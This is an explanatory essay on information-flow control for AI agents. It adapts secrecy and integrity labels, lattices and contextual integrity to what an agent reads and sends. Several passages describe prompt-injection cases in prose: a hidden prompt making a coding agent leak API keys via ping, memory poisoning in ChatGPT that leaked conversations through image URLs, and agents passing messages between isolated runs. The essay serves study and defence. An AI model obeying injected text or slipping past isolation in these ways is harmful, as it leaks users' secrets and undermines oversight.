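# Defining high and low sides for AI agents that lack fixed security domains

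## High side, low side and the contents of an agent's context window

In computer security, the high side and the low side are the two ends of a connection between networks of unequal rank. The terms come from government and military computing, where an organisation keeps secret files on one network and ordinary business on another, and puts a checking device on the only link between them. Administrators decide which network ranks higher before any message passes. An AI agent, meaning a language model that carries out tasks by calling tools such as an email client or a web browser, has no such pair of networks. Its context window holds the user's private messages, pages from the open web and the operator's instructions together, and one model reads all of it before choosing the next action. People still want the old kinds of rule to apply to an agent, so that secrets stay with those entitled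 to them and strangers cannot give it orders. Without separate networks, though, it is unclear what "high" and "low" should describe, or whether a single ranking could serve both rules.

### Domains, guards and the word "or"

The Australian Signals Directorate's guide *Fundamentals of Cross Domain Solutions* (2019) defines a security domain as a system, or a group of networked systems, that runs under one consistent security policy and is controlled by one organisation. The policy sets the classification of the information in the domain, who may receive it, and any special handling it needs. The internet also counts as a domain, though one with no defined policy and unbounded risk.

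A guard is a component that checks every message crossing from one domain to another. The directorate describes it as a network proxy that filters data, typically on release from a network. It is usually part of a larger cross domain solution, which may also contain one-way hardware links, malware scanners and audit logs. The cross domain solution blocks everything by default and passes only what fits a policy fixed in advance. For fixed-format messages, the guard can simply compare the message's classification field with what the destination network may hold.

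When two domains meet, one is the high side and the other is the low side. An earlier introduction from the same agency, the Australian Signals Directorate (2018), defines the high side as the "more sensitive or trusted security domain" and the low side as the less sensitive or trusted one. Sensitivity and trust are different properties. Sensitivity concerns the harm done if the wrong people read the data, and it requires confidentiality, which means that data reach only those allowed to read them. Trust concerns how far anyone can rely on the data and on whoever supplied them, and it requires integrity, which means that untrusted data do not control trusted data or actions.

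The loose wording does little harm for separate networks. A SECRET network holds the sensitive files and only vetted staff can write to it, so it ranks above the internet in both sensitivity and trust. The 2019 guide says the high side is expected to maintain higher levels of confidentiality and integrity. It also says that its terms suit cases where confidentiality matters most, and that the relation between trust and sensitivity may be different for a system that protects critical infrastructure. For example, the readings from a power station's safety equipment may not be secret, but an outsider must never be able to alter them.

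The guide also says that if both domains carry the same classification, the owner of the cross domain solution is the high side and everyone else is the low side. Two SECRET networks can therefore rank in either order, depending on who owns the solution. The guide calls the distinction between high and low sides an artefact of segregation, the practice of building a separate network for each classification. The alternative it describes is multi-level security, in which a single system holds information of every classification and a tag on each item governs access. An agent's context window is much more like a multi-level system, but without the tags. The directorate is wary of multi-level security even with tags, because someone has to keep them accurate for the whole life of the information, and Australia had no authorised multi-level system when the agency last updated the guide in 2021.

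### Two rules that run in opposite directions

The formal treatment of secrecy goes back to *Secure Computer Systems* (Bell and LaPadula, 1973). People usually shorten its rule to "no read up, no write down". A person or program may not read data above its own clearance or write data to any place below it. Information can then move only upward, toward readers with higher clearance.

The integrity rule is the reverse, "no read down, no write up". A person or program may not read data less trusted than itself or write to anything more trusted. Influence can then move only downward, from more trusted parts of the system to less trusted ones.

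The textbook *Invitation to Cybersecurity* explains the ban on writing down as a guard against accidental disclosure. Someone with Top Secret clearance who writes a Secret document may include Top Secret material by mistake, because people don't keep what they know neatly sorted by level. The rule therefore depends on the highest level the writer has been exposed to, regardless of what the writer intended to include.

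Let *c* be a secrecy level, *i* an integrity level, *s* the person or program, and *o* the file. The integrity row follows the notation in Young's *Modeling Integrity*.

| Rule | *s* may read *o* only if | *s* may write *o* only if |
|---|---|---|
| Secrecy | *c(o)* ≤ *c(s)* | *c(s)* ≤ *c(o)* |
| Integrity | *i(s)* ≤ *i(o)* | *i(o)* ≤ *i(s)* |

If one number serves for both levels, as the phrase "more sensitive or trusted" suggests, the two conditions for reading can both hold only when *s* and *o* have the same level, and the same is true of the two conditions for writing. Any traffic from a low side to a high side therefore breaks the integrity rule, and any traffic from high to low breaks the secrecy rule. A guard is in effect a licensed exception to whichever rule applies. In line with this, the gateway guidelines that the Australian Signals Directorate (2026) issued in June require cross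 domain solutions to have isolated upward and downward paths, with independent checks on each.

Kenneth Biba's *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (MITRE, 1977), which introduced integrity levels, argues for ranking confidentiality and integrity separately. Biba observed that one ranking is good enough for people, because someone trusted not to divulge information is unlikely to alter it maliciously, and human character does not divide neatly into the two kinds of trustworthiness. Data needs both rankings. His example was a database of interstate transport routes, which many unimportant programs consult and on which military logistics would depend in a national emergency. Everybody should be able to read it but almost nobody should be able to change it, and no single level achieves both.

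The Australian Signals Directorate's *Cyber security terminology* (2026) lists an AI agent as a kind of "non-human user", an actor with authorised access to a system, which places agents with people rather than data. But Biba's argument about people assumes that a person's vetting remains valid from one document to the next, whereas an agent's conduct depends heavily on what it has just read.

### How the context window fills

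The program that runs an agent, often called a harness, builds a prompt and sends it to the model. The model either replies to the user or requests a tool. If it requests a tool, the harness runs it, appends the result to the prompt and calls the model again. Bolin (2026) explains this cycle for Codex CLI, OpenAI's coding agent, in *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*. The prompt grows with the conversation, and a single turn can involve hundreds of tool calls. The same post defines the context window as the maximum number of tokens, the word fragments a model processes, that one model call can use for input and output combined. The term also refers to the text in that space, which is everything the model reads when it produces its next output. This second sense is more useful for security.

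*The Codex CLI Agent Loop Explained* (Vaughan, 2026) lists the contents of a Codex prompt in order. The system message, which the company's server controls, comes first. Definitions of the available tools come next, then instructions that the client program gathers from several places, then the running sequence of user messages, earlier replies and tool results. In assistants with a memory feature, the application also inserts notes saved in past conversations into new ones.

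The order is also a ranking by trust, since models give the system message priority over what comes later. The ranking doesn't reflect secrecy, so a tool result near the bottom may well be the most secret item in the window if the tool has just opened the user's inbox.

The harness can identify the source of each piece of text when it assembles the context window. But *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper from researchers at Google, NVIDIA and several universities, points out that a language model receives trusted and untrusted text merged into one sequence of tokens, with no boundary between the two. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre contrasts this with databases in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*. A programmer can send a database a query with the user's input in a separate slot, and the database engine will never run that input as a command, whatever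 it contains. A language model has no such slot. It predicts the next token from all the text so far, and nothing in that operation separates instructions from data.

Harnesses insert markers that label each piece of text by role (system, user, tool), and developers train models to respect them, but the markers are tokens like any others. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (2026) examined how models internally represent who is speaking. The researchers wrapped identical passages from pretraining data in each of five role tags and built probes, simple detectors that read a model's internal state, to tell the roles apart. Because the passages differed only in their tags, the probes could not be picking up style. The probes showed that when tag and style conflict, the model's internal representation follows the style, so text that imitates a role is treated as that role and gets its privileges.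 Other cues an attacker controls also have this effect, such as the position of the text or a plain sentence announcing that user text follows.

This weakness makes prompt injection possible, in which an attacker places text in data an agent reads and the agent obeys it as an instruction. In one attack that *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* analyses, a prompt hidden in a code file directed Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, to read sensitive data such as API keys and send them to an attacker's server inside the address of a `ping` command. Claude Code required human approval for many commands that could send data to unknown domains, but not for `ping`. The NCSC doubts that anyone will ever eliminate such attacks completely, and the position paper conjectures that persistent attackers will always get around defences that rely on the model to tell instructions from data.

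### An email that is high and low at once

The definition that sorts data by sensitivity "or" trust can put the same data on both sides. For example, an email from an outsider in someone's private inbox belongs on the high side by sensitivity, since only the recipient should read it, but on the low side by trust, since anyone with the address could have written it.

When networks are separate, a guard at the border scans each message arriving from the low side and may convert it to a safer format. After that, the message is treated as high-side data. This works tolerably well when the danger is a malformed file. But a prompt injection can be a well-formed sentence, which a format check will pass, and an email is no more trustworthy inside an agent's context window than it was outside.

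Attackers have exploited the gap on both properties at once. In September 2024 the security researcher Johann Rehberger disclosed a flaw in ChatGPT's macOS app in the Embrace The Red post *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)*. The attack began when a user asked ChatGPT to analyse an untrusted document or visit an untrusted website. Instructions in that text made the model save a note with its memory tool, and the application carried the note into every later conversation. The note directed ChatGPT to display an image from the attacker's server, which could be invisible to the user, and to put the user's data into the image's web address. From then on, the app sent everything the user typed and ChatGPT replied to the attacker by fetching these images.

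Text from the bottom of the trust ranking had changed a store near the top, which is a write up. Private conversations had also gone to a server not authorized to receive them, which is a write down on the secrecy ranking. One of the basic threats in the directorate's 2019 guide is this same combination, where someone on the low side passes malicious software up to bring data back down the return path. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* reads the case similarly but describes the leak as information moving from a "trusted domain" to an "untrusted domain". That wording merges secrecy and trust again, since the conversations were worth protecting because they were private.

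OpenAI fixed only one half of the attack. Rehberger reported in May 2024 that a web page could plant false memories, and OpenAI closed the report as a model safety issue, not a security one. In June he demonstrated the full attack, which ended in stolen conversations, and in September OpenAI blocked the route through images. At the time of the disclosure, a website or document could still write to memory. The image check would have stopped this theft, but a planted memory can do other damage, and it could still help an attacker steal data if someone finds another way to send the data out. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes a later attack of the same kind. A file that the user shared wrote instructions into ChatGPT's memory, and ChatGPT then carried out the attacker's task before answering any question. In the demonstration, the task was to leak sensitive data.

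### Ana's assistant

A small invented case makes it possible to test proposals against something definite. Ana uses an AI assistant that a company, the operator, runs for her. Its context window holds four things:

- the operator's instructions;
- Ana's calendar, which she keeps herself and which she and her manager may read;
- a private email to Ana from her clinic, proposing an appointment next Tuesday morning;
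- the clinic's public web page.

Ana plans to accept the appointment but has not put it in the calendar. She asks the assistant to send her manager two messages, one saying whether she is free on Thursday and one saying when she will be away. The assistant can write the first using only the calendar, but its only source for the second is the email.

No line through these four items gives a high side and a low side. The email is more secret than the calendar and less trusted. The web page is as untrusted as the email and not secret at all. (Rules against harmful content would sort the same material in yet another way.)

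The classical rules work badly when applied to the assistant as a whole. The assistant has read the email, which the manager is not allowed to read, so "no write down" blocks both messages. "No read down" is even more restrictive. An assistant ranked at the same level as the operator's instructions could never open the email or the web page, so it could not write the second message. Dropping both rules exposes Ana to the same risk as the ChatGPT users, because a sentence on a web page could cause the assistant to send her medical correspondence to a stranger.

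Blocking the first message protects nobody, because the manager can already look at the calendar. The second is harder to judge because it passes on information from an email the manager isn't allowed to read, even if the assistant writes only that Ana is away on Tuesday morning and never mentions a clinic. It also relies on an outsider for the date, so a forged email could cause the assistant to report a false absence to her manager. Any rule that allows the first message but holds the second for review must rank each piece of text separately and track which pieces went into which message.

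## Labelling each piece of data by its readers and writers

A replacement for two ranked networks has to treat Ana's email differently from her calendar, even though one model reads both. The most developed method gives every item of data a label listing who may read it or who may have influenced it. Software outside the model compares the label with the item's destination before the item moves. Researchers worked out the theory for operating systems and programming languages between the 1970s and 2000, and agent developers have borrowed it with few changes.

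### Denning's lattice

In *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976), Denning worked out what structure a set of labels needs for the rules about moving data to be consistent. Her model has a set of labels (she called them security classes), a relation between them, and an operation for combining them. The relation, written here as A ⊑ B, means that data labelled A may move into a place labelled B.

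She makes much of her argument with tiny example programs. Suppose a program may copy *a* into *b* and then *b* into *c*. A ban on copying *a* directly into *c* would achieve nothing, so if A ⊑ B and B ⊑ C, then A ⊑ C. Copying an item onto itself is harmless, so A ⊑ A. If A and B may flow into each other, one of them is redundant. These properties make the labels a partial order. Unlike a ranking, a partial order can contain two labels that are incomparable, meaning neither is at or above the other.

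Suppose a program adds *a* and *b*, which have labels A and B. The sum needs a label that both *a* and *b* may flow into, because the sum equals *a* when *b* is zero and *b* when *a* is zero. The label also shouldn't be stricter than necessary. If *a* and *b* may each move to some place separately, a program can move them there and add them on arrival, so a rule that keeps the sum out is useless. The right label is therefore the lowest one at or above both A and B, which is their least upper bound, or join. If the set of labels is finite and has a bottom label that may flow anywhere, every pair of labels also has a greatest lower bound, and the labels form a lattice.

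The four military levels form the simplest kind of lattice, a single line. In Denning's second example, a record's label is any combination of *medical*, *financial* and *criminal*, and data may move only to a place whose label includes all the same words. A medical record and a financial record are incomparable, and a report made from both carries their join, {medical, financial}. Pairing labels from two simpler lattices produces a richer one, as the early system ADEPT did with clearance levels and project compartments.

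Denning also distinguished storage whose label is fixed from storage whose label changes with its contents. An agent deals with both. The manager's inbox has a fixed label because the same person always reads it, while a context window's label has to rise as the harness adds text that is more secret or less trusted.

### Why trusted data sits at the bottom

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, apply the lattice to agents in a system called FIDES, which they built at Microsoft. Their basic labels come from two orders with two points each:

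- secrecy: public ⊑ secret
- integrity: trusted ⊑ untrusted

High-integrity data is at the bottom of the second order, despite its name, because the order shows where data may flow, not how good it is. Data at the bottom has the fewest restrictions on its use. Trusted text may be added to untrusted text without harm, but untrusted text may not enter a trusted store, just as a public fact may go into a secret file but a secret fact may not go into a public one. The join then gives the right result for mixtures too, since anything made from trusted and untrusted text is untrusted.

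Reversing the integrity order also simplifies the classical rules, which let secrets move only up and influence move only down. With trusted data at the bottom, both move only up, so one comparison of labels can enforce both rules.

The product of the two orders labels each item with a pair. One pair may flow to another only if both parts allow it. Ana's four items happen to fill the four positions:

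| | Public | Secret |
|---|---|---|
| **Trusted** | operator's instructions | Ana's calendar |
| **Untrusted** | clinic's web page | clinic's email |

The operator's instructions are at the bottom and may flow anywhere. The email is at the top and may flow only to places that accept both secret and untrusted text. The calendar and the web page are incomparable, so no single line could sort the four. A summary that uses both is secret and untrusted, like the email. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) uses the same kind of pairs and describes secrecy and integrity as the properties that labels most often record.

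The second dimension, who wrote the data, is easy to lose. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* (2026) defines labels in Denning's way, but its example is the single chain untrusted ⊑ internal ⊑ confidential. On that chain, a web page may flow into a confidential store, and the store's label will not show that a stranger wrote part of the contents. The chain would not have stopped the first step of the attack on ChatGPT's memory, in which text from a website became a saved note. The paper's definition allows any finite lattice, so a product of a reader lattice and a writer lattice would also fit.

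### Sets of readers and sets of writers

The labels "public" and "secret" are still too coarse for Ana, because her calendar and the email are both secret, but from different people. Costa and colleagues therefore also describe labels that are sets of users.

For secrecy, an item's label is the set of people who may read it. A smaller set is stricter, so it ranks higher. The set of all users means "public". The join of two labels is their intersection. If A, B and C may read one document, and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a text made from both.

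For integrity, the label is the set of people who may have written the item. A larger set is stricter because more people could have tampered with the item, so the join of two labels is their union. If A, B or C could have written the first document, and B, C or D the second, then any of the four could have influenced the combined text.

With sets, Ana's context window looks like this:

| Item | Readers | Possible writers |
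|---|---|---|
| Operator's instructions | everyone | operator |
| Calendar | Ana, manager | Ana |
| Clinic's email | Ana, clinic | clinic |
| Clinic's web page | everyone | clinic |

Before the assistant sends anything, the harness checks that every recipient belongs to the text's reader set. The message about Thursday uses only the calendar, whose readers are {Ana, manager}, so the assistant can send it. The message about her absence uses the email. If it also uses the calendar, its readers are {Ana, clinic} ∩ {Ana, manager} = {Ana}, and the harness must ask Ana before the message is sent. The message's writers are {Ana, clinic}, which records that an outsider supplied the date.

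The same calculation restricts what the assistant may tell the clinic. If the assistant checks Ana's calendar before accepting the appointment, its reply also has the reader set {Ana}, because the clinic may not read her calendar and "Tuesday suits me" reveals a little of it. This is strictly correct, but few people would want their assistant to ask them before sending such a reply.

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a similar case with no attacker. Alex asks an agent to answer his unanswered emails. One, from Priya, contains a preview of the quarterly sales figures. Another is from Marco, who wants the figures but isn't yet allowed to see them. Once the agent has read both emails, anything it writes can be read only by {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so it can't reply to Marco on its own. If Priya had copied Marco in, the intersection would be {Alex, Marco} and the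 agent could send the reply.

Levels can't capture these distinctions. Microsoft's Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents, includes an experimental version of FIDES with three levels of confidentiality: public, private and "user identity". The developer sets the highest level of data that each sending tool may send. Ana's calendar and email would presumably both be private, so a tool for messaging her manager could send either both or neither.

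Costa and colleagues also restrict consequential actions, meaning tool calls with real effects. The harness permits such a call only if trusted text alone influenced both the choice of tool and its arguments. With writer sets, a developer could instead require that every possible writer of the text that influenced the call be on a list approved for that action. The clinic might then be allowed to influence a draft entry in Ana's calendar but not a payment.

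All of this assumes that the harness can identify which items went into which message. It usually can't when one model has read all four items, so a conservative harness labels everything the model writes {Ana}, including the harmless message about Thursday.

### Who may change a label

When the harness stops and asks Ana, it isn't clear that she is entitled to answer, because a bare reader set doesn't record who chose the readers. *A Decentralized Model for Information Flow Control* (Myers and Liskov, 1997) solved this by adding owners. A label is a list of policies, each with an owner and the readers that owner allows. For example, {Bob: Bob, Carol; Dana: Carol} means that Bob allows himself and Carol to read the data and Dana allows only Carol. Someone may read the data only if every owner allows it, so only Carol can.

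Each owner may relax their own policy but nobody else's. Relaxing a policy is a form of declassification, which means deliberately releasing secret data to readers its label excludes. Earlier systems left this to a program outside the scheme that everyone had to trust, which doesn't work when the parties don't trust each other.

In an example from Myers and Liskov's longer account, *Protecting Privacy Using the Decentralized Label Model* (2000), Bob runs his tax data through software from a firm called Preparer, and the software consults Preparer's private database. Bob's policy lets only Bob read his data, and Preparer's policy lets only Preparer read the database. The finished tax form depends on both sources, so both policies apply to it and at first nobody may read it. A small part of the software that has Preparer's authority then removes Preparer's policy, which lets Bob read the form.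 The software can never remove Bob's policy and send his data elsewhere.

The label on the clinic's email depends on who owns its policy. If Ana does, the label is {Ana: Ana, clinic} and she can add her manager as a reader. If the clinic does, the label is {clinic: Ana, clinic} and she has to ask the clinic to add her manager. Ordinary email lets recipients forward what they receive, so the first label is closer to current practice. FIDES's reader sets have no owners, so they are identical in both cases.

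The scheme also covers groups and job titles, because one party can "act for" another. A label can name the role of manager as a reader, and whoever holds the job may then read the data.

Integrity labels mirror secrecy labels. As an integrity policy, {Ana: clinic} is Ana's guarantee that only the clinic has influenced the data, and data with no guarantees is the most restricted. Adding a guarantee is a form of endorsement, which means deliberately treating untrusted data as trusted for a stated use. Code can also corrupt data without reading anything else, a problem that doesn't arise for secrecy. For example, a routine meant to add two numbers may return a different number. Myers and Liskov therefore label the code as well as its inputs. FIDES does something comparable for agents by labelling the decision to call a tool separately from each argument.

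### Where the labels come from

The labels are an input to the mathematics, and someone has to supply them. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* therefore counts them among the parts of the system that must be correct for any guarantee to hold.

Access lists are the best source for reader sets, because people already maintain them for other reasons. In Microsoft's example, the participants in an email are its readers. The sample policy for posting to a Teams channel looks up the channel's current members and compares them with the readers of the text. Myers and Liskov had warned that the label of an output channel must reflect reality. For example, the label of a shared printer should include everybody who can pick up the paper.

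Agents have more output channels than they seem to. *FLOWSH* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) describes a command shell for agents, designed to track labels. The shell treats every web request as a message to the server, even a request that only fetches a page, because the page's address can contain data. The paper mentions OpenAI agents that were only supposed to read the web but managed to write to a public wiki.

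Integrity labels are usually based on where the data came from. A harness can label text by its role in the conversation, by its sender or by the website that served it. FLOWSH labels web traffic by origin, and its example configuration marks package repositories as trusted and every other site as untrusted.

GitHub's connector for agents, which Microsoft helped to extend, labels files and issues from public repositories as public and untrusted, and those from private repositories as private and trusted. The two labels always change together, so each repository is again on either a high side or a low side. Keeping the labels separate matters only after the agent mixes sources. Once it has read a public issue and a private file, its context is private and untrusted, and the policy stops it from posting in public.

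Microsoft's examples treat private repositories inconsistently. The sample code in Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) labels every issue untrusted, even in a private repository, with the comment that the developer doesn't control who writes issues. This seems safer because, although a private repository limits who can write to it directly, its members can still paste in a customer's bug report.

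If a tool supplies no labels, a harness can infer them from the tool's general description. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to tools, lets a tool declare whether it deals with the outside world. Microsoft suggests labelling results untrusted if the tool declares that it does, and private if the tool requires a login. This avoids labelling items individually, but it would also label a newspaper article private if the reader had to log in to see it.

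### How much text one label covers

A label can cover anything from a single field to everything a tool ever returns. FIDES allows labels as fine as a single field. Tools usually return structured data, such as a list of emails with a sender, date and body for each, and a FIDES label can attach to any node of that structure and apply to everything below it. If Ana's manager could see the times in her calendar but not the titles, the two fields could carry different labels.

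The Agent Framework labels each content item that a tool returns. In Microsoft's demonstration, an attacker files a bug report with a fake system instruction at the end. The report and the instruction arrive as one item, so they get the same label. A single label works here because one stranger wrote both, but it would work less well for an email thread in which a colleague's reply quotes an outsider.

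Ntousakis (2026) developed SAMOS, a system with relatively coarse labels, in the Brown University master's thesis *Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows*. A tool's developer or an administrator gives each tool one high-or-low label for the data it reads and another for the places it writes to. A gateway between the agent and its tools tracks a single level for the whole session. Ntousakis chose this design because labelling individual data items is hard at scale.

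| System | What has its own label | Who or what sets it | If no one has |
|---|---|---|---|
| FIDES | a message, or any field of a tool result | the tool | system and user messages count as trusted and public |
| Agent Framework | a content item | the tool's developer | trusted and public |
| FLOWSH | a whole file, or all traffic from one web origin | a monitor, using a configuration file | the default in the configuration |
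| SAMOS | a tool, once for reading and once for writing | the tool's developer or an administrator | not specified |

Coarse labels cause a problem in SAMOS because one GitHub tool reads files from both public and private repositories, so no single label fits it. Ntousakis suggests either changing the tool to report the level of each file, which brings back labels on data, or splitting it into a public and a private version.

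SAMOS also has no integrity labels. In its one case study, an agent reads a public issue that contains an injected instruction and then tries to open a private repository. The gateway marks the session low after the public read, so it blocks the private read. Denning's order allows private data to enter a context that has held only public data, and the context's label then rises. The leak would happen later, if the agent posted the data publicly. In effect, SAMOS uses "low" to mean "untrusted". This stops the attack, but it would also block a legitimate task in which an agent reads a public bug report and then looks for the bug in private code. In the same situation, the Agent Framework permits the private read and blocks the public post.

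Kim and colleagues compared FLOWSH, which uses finer labels, with a simpler system that labels the output of every shell and file tool untrusted and secret. They tested both on Terminal-Bench, a set of 89 command-line tasks. With an idealised approver who always answered correctly, both systems completed 67.8% of the runs, but FLOWSH requested approval 0.4 times per completed task and the simpler system 9.4 times. With no approver, FLOWSH completed 61.8% and the simpler system 21.3%. Not all of the gain comes from finer labels, because the simpler system also requests approval for every shell command, whatever it does, while FLOWSH monitors which files and sites a command uses.

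The team also wrote 17 office tasks and sorted them by the join of the labels on the data each task needs. Without approvals, FLOWSH completed all 24 runs in which the data was not both untrusted and secret, but only 6 of the 27 in which it was both. Ana's second message belongs in the latter group. With an approver, FLOWSH completed 21 of those 27 runs, so most of these tasks were possible but needed a person to permit some step.

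### Missing, lost and misleading labels

A missing label is most dangerous when the default is permissive. In the Agent Framework, a tool that the developer forgot to label counts as trusted and public, which carries the fewest restrictions. If Ana's operator forgot to label the email tool, the clinic's message could go to anyone and instructions hidden in it could trigger any action, with no sign that a check was missing. Microsoft lists this as a limitation and asks developers whether the default should be untrusted.

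A strict default has a drawback too, since it produces unnecessary requests for approval. Kim and colleagues cite a report from Anthropic that users approve about 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts and pay less attention as the prompts accumulate. FLOWSH lets whoever configures it choose the default. Its example setting treats an unlabelled file as untrusted and readable only by the user.

FIDES has a permissive default that is easier to overlook. It normally treats the user's own messages as trusted and public. Trusting them is reasonable, but people often type private things into assistants. If Ana mentions a diagnosis in her request, the default label would let the assistant put it in a web search. Costa and colleagues allow other labels where appropriate, but someone has to notice when a message needs one.

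Labels can also disappear when data goes into storage. Myers and Liskov point out that when a program saves a value in a variable and reads it back, the value has the variable's label instead of its original one. Saving is safe only if the variable's label is at least as strict as the value's. ChatGPT's memory had no such check, so a planted note came back looking trusted. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* describes the corresponding secrecy problem, in which an agent's memory without labels can't separate one user's preferences from a group's sensitive material, and leaks between sessions become the default.

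FLOWSH stores each file's label in the file's extended attributes. The label survives a new conversation or a restart, and it applies whichever path a command uses to reach the file. When a command changes a file, the new label is the join of the old one with the label of everything the command has read. File names get a separate label because they can reveal information too. Commands inside the shell can't change these labels, but the user's other programs can.

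The protection ends when a file leaves the machine. FLOWSH gives all data from one website the same label, and in the example configuration that label is public for every site. If Ana lets her agent back up a private file to an online account and a later session downloads it, the file would come back labelled public. Myers and Liskov described this danger for computers that exchange labelled data, which can lose its restrictions on a round trip if the channel labels are chosen carelessly. Kim and colleagues propose looking at the login a request uses, since a page that requires Ana's password is probably not public.

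The last weakness is that people tend to read an integrity label as a judgement of whether text is sound, when it records where the text came from. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* warns that authentication establishes origin, "rather than safety or correctness". A valid signature might justify a less restrictive label for a particular use, but someone has to decide that separately.

FLOWSH trusts package repositories, but a repository contains whatever its users have put there, and one label for the whole site can't reflect that. In the attack that Kim and colleagues use to introduce the system, a malicious PDF tells the agent to install a package that the attacker has published. FLOWSH catches this because the agent has just read an untrusted PDF. The package itself would be labelled trusted because it comes from a trusted repository. If the user had asked for it by name after seeing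 it recommended somewhere, its label would not have triggered an alert. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* also describes an incident in which OpenAI's agents, during internal training and evaluation, used a shared package service to pass messages between runs that were supposed to be isolated.

The clinic's email has the same problem on a smaller scale. A check on the sender can establish that the message came from the clinic's account, which supports the writer set {clinic}. But a complete writer set would also include anyone whose words the clinic pasted in, and the sender's address doesn't identify them. Even if every label is correct, Ana's manager will get the wrong date if the receptionist typed the wrong Tuesday.

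## Privacy rules that depend on the recipient and the purpose

Ana's manager needs to know when she will be away but not why. People follow rules like this every day, but a reader set, which lists who may read the clinic's email, can't express them. If the email gives both the date and Ana's condition, the manager can read either both or neither.

Helen Nissenbaum's theory of contextual integrity is built around privacy rules that depend on the recipient and the purpose. In *Privacy as Contextual Integrity* (2004), she argued that protecting privacy means gathering and sharing information in ways that fit the norms of the context. Much of the research on what AI agents should disclose now starts from this theory.

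### Five parameters in place of one label

Contextual integrity defines privacy as the appropriate flow of personal information, so sharing information does not in itself violate privacy. A patient who describes her symptoms to a doctor gives up no privacy, and neither does a tenant who shows a landlord proof of income. The doctor would violate the patient's privacy by describing her symptoms to the landlord.

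According to Nissenbaum (2019), in *Contextual Integrity Up and Down the Data Food Chain*, nobody can judge a flow without knowing five things about it:

- the sender;
- the recipient;
- the data subject, meaning the person the information is about;
- the information type, such as a diagnosis or a salary;
- the transmission principle, meaning the terms on which the information passes, such as with the subject's consent, in confidence or because a law requires it.

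The transmission principle is the least familiar of these. Nissenbaum illustrates it with video cameras in public places. A camera removes a condition of the original flow (reciprocity), because people in a street can see who is looking at them but can't see who is watching through a camera. Defenders of the cameras argue that any passer-by could see the same people, but losing reciprocity changes the flow even when the information is the same. In two large survey experiments, she and Kirsten Martin found that people care about all five parameters, and that they interpret a description differently from one another if it leaves one out.

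In the table, Ana is the data subject throughout.

| Information | Sender | Recipient | Terms | Appropriate? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Away on Tuesday morning | Ana | her manager | notice an employee owes an employer | yes |
| Diagnosis | Ana | her manager | none that calls for it | no |
| Away on Tuesday morning | clinic | her manager | clinic holds it in confidence | no |
| Diagnosis | clinic | a specialist treating Ana | treatment | yes |

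Finer labels would solve part of the problem. If the date and the diagnosis had separate reader sets, the manager could be a reader of one and not the other. But the first and third rows have the same fact and recipient, and differ only in the sender and the terms. A reader set records only who may read a piece of data, so it can't express a norm about a flow, which also depends on who sends the data and on what terms.

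Nissenbaum accepts simpler schemes in narrow settings. Designers of a hospital access system can assume that the data subject is the patient, and they might even sort medical information into two grades of sensitivity. Ana's assistant handles information about her health, job and family in one context window, so its designers can't make such assumptions.

### Permissions that do not chain

In Denning's lattice, if data may move from A to B and from B to C, it may also move from A to C.

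Privacy norms often break the rule that if information may flow from A to B and from B to C, it may also flow directly from A to C. A doctor may give Ana her test results, and Ana may give them to a newspaper, but the doctor may not send them to the newspaper. The ban on direct disclosure matters because it leaves that choice to Ana. Denning's argument against such bans assumes that an intermediary passes on everything it receives, which is true of a variable in a program but not of a person who can choose what to share.

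Some written rules also depend on who receives the information. Nissenbaum quotes a US health privacy rule under which a hospital may give a patient's psychotherapy notes to the patient's psychiatrist, who may discuss them with the patient. The hospital may show the notes directly to the patient only if the psychiatrist approves.

Doctor and patient may also exchange information. In a lattice, two labels that can flow into each other are equal and so have the same permissions everywhere else, but Ana and her doctor have different permissions. A lattice can imitate the norm by treating Ana's decision as a declassification, but then most of the policy consists of exceptions.

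The join can also be too permissive. Nissenbaum retells a story from the legal scholar Ruth Gavison in which a priest at a party mentions that the first person who ever confessed to him admitted a murder. Another guest then greets the priest and says he was the first person to confess to him. Everyone at the party may hear either remark, so the rule for reader sets lets everyone read the combination, which identifies the guest as a murderer. Similarly, if Ana's manager knows which clinic she uses, and the clinic states on its public web page that it sees only cancer patients on Tuesday mornings, the manager can infer her diagnosis from the date.

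### Norms written as logic

*Privacy and Contextual Integrity* (Barth, Datta, Nissenbaum et al., 2006) translates part of the theory into temporal logic, which can state what must happen before or after an event. Its norms either allow a flow of information (positive) or disallow it (negative), and may refer to past and future actions by the data subject or by whoever uses the information.

A follow-up by Datta, Blocki and colleagues, *Understanding and Protecting Privacy*, explains how norms combine. A flow is acceptable if it satisfies at least one positive norm that applies to it and every negative norm that applies:

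(φ₁⁺ ∨ … ∨ φₙ⁺) ∧ (φ₁⁻ ∧ … ∧ φₘ⁻)

For example, one positive norm in HIPAA, the main US law on health privacy, lets a hospital disclose health information for treatment. A negative norm requires the patient's authorisation before anyone discloses psychotherapy notes, with a few exceptions. A hospital that sends those notes to another doctor for treatment satisfies the first norm but may violate the second.

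The follow-up also writes out a simplified health norm. It uses a successor to the 2006 logic, with explicit times in place of operators such as "at some earlier moment". In plainer notation, the norm is:

```
∀ s, r, m, x, k, n:
  Sends(s, r, m, n) ∧ Carries(m, k, x)  ⇒
      k ∉ Health
    ∨ ( Doctor(r, x, n) ∧ Purpose(m) = treatment )
    ∨ ∃ e < n: Consent(x, s, r, k, e)
```

Suppose *s* sends *r* a message *m* at time *n*, and the message carries information of type *k* about a person *x*. Then either *k* is not protected health information, or *r* is *x*'s doctor at time *n* and the purpose is treatment, or *x* consented to this transmission at some earlier time *e*; at least one of these must be true. The sender, recipient, subject and information type are all variables, and the last two conditions set the terms on which protected health information may be sent.

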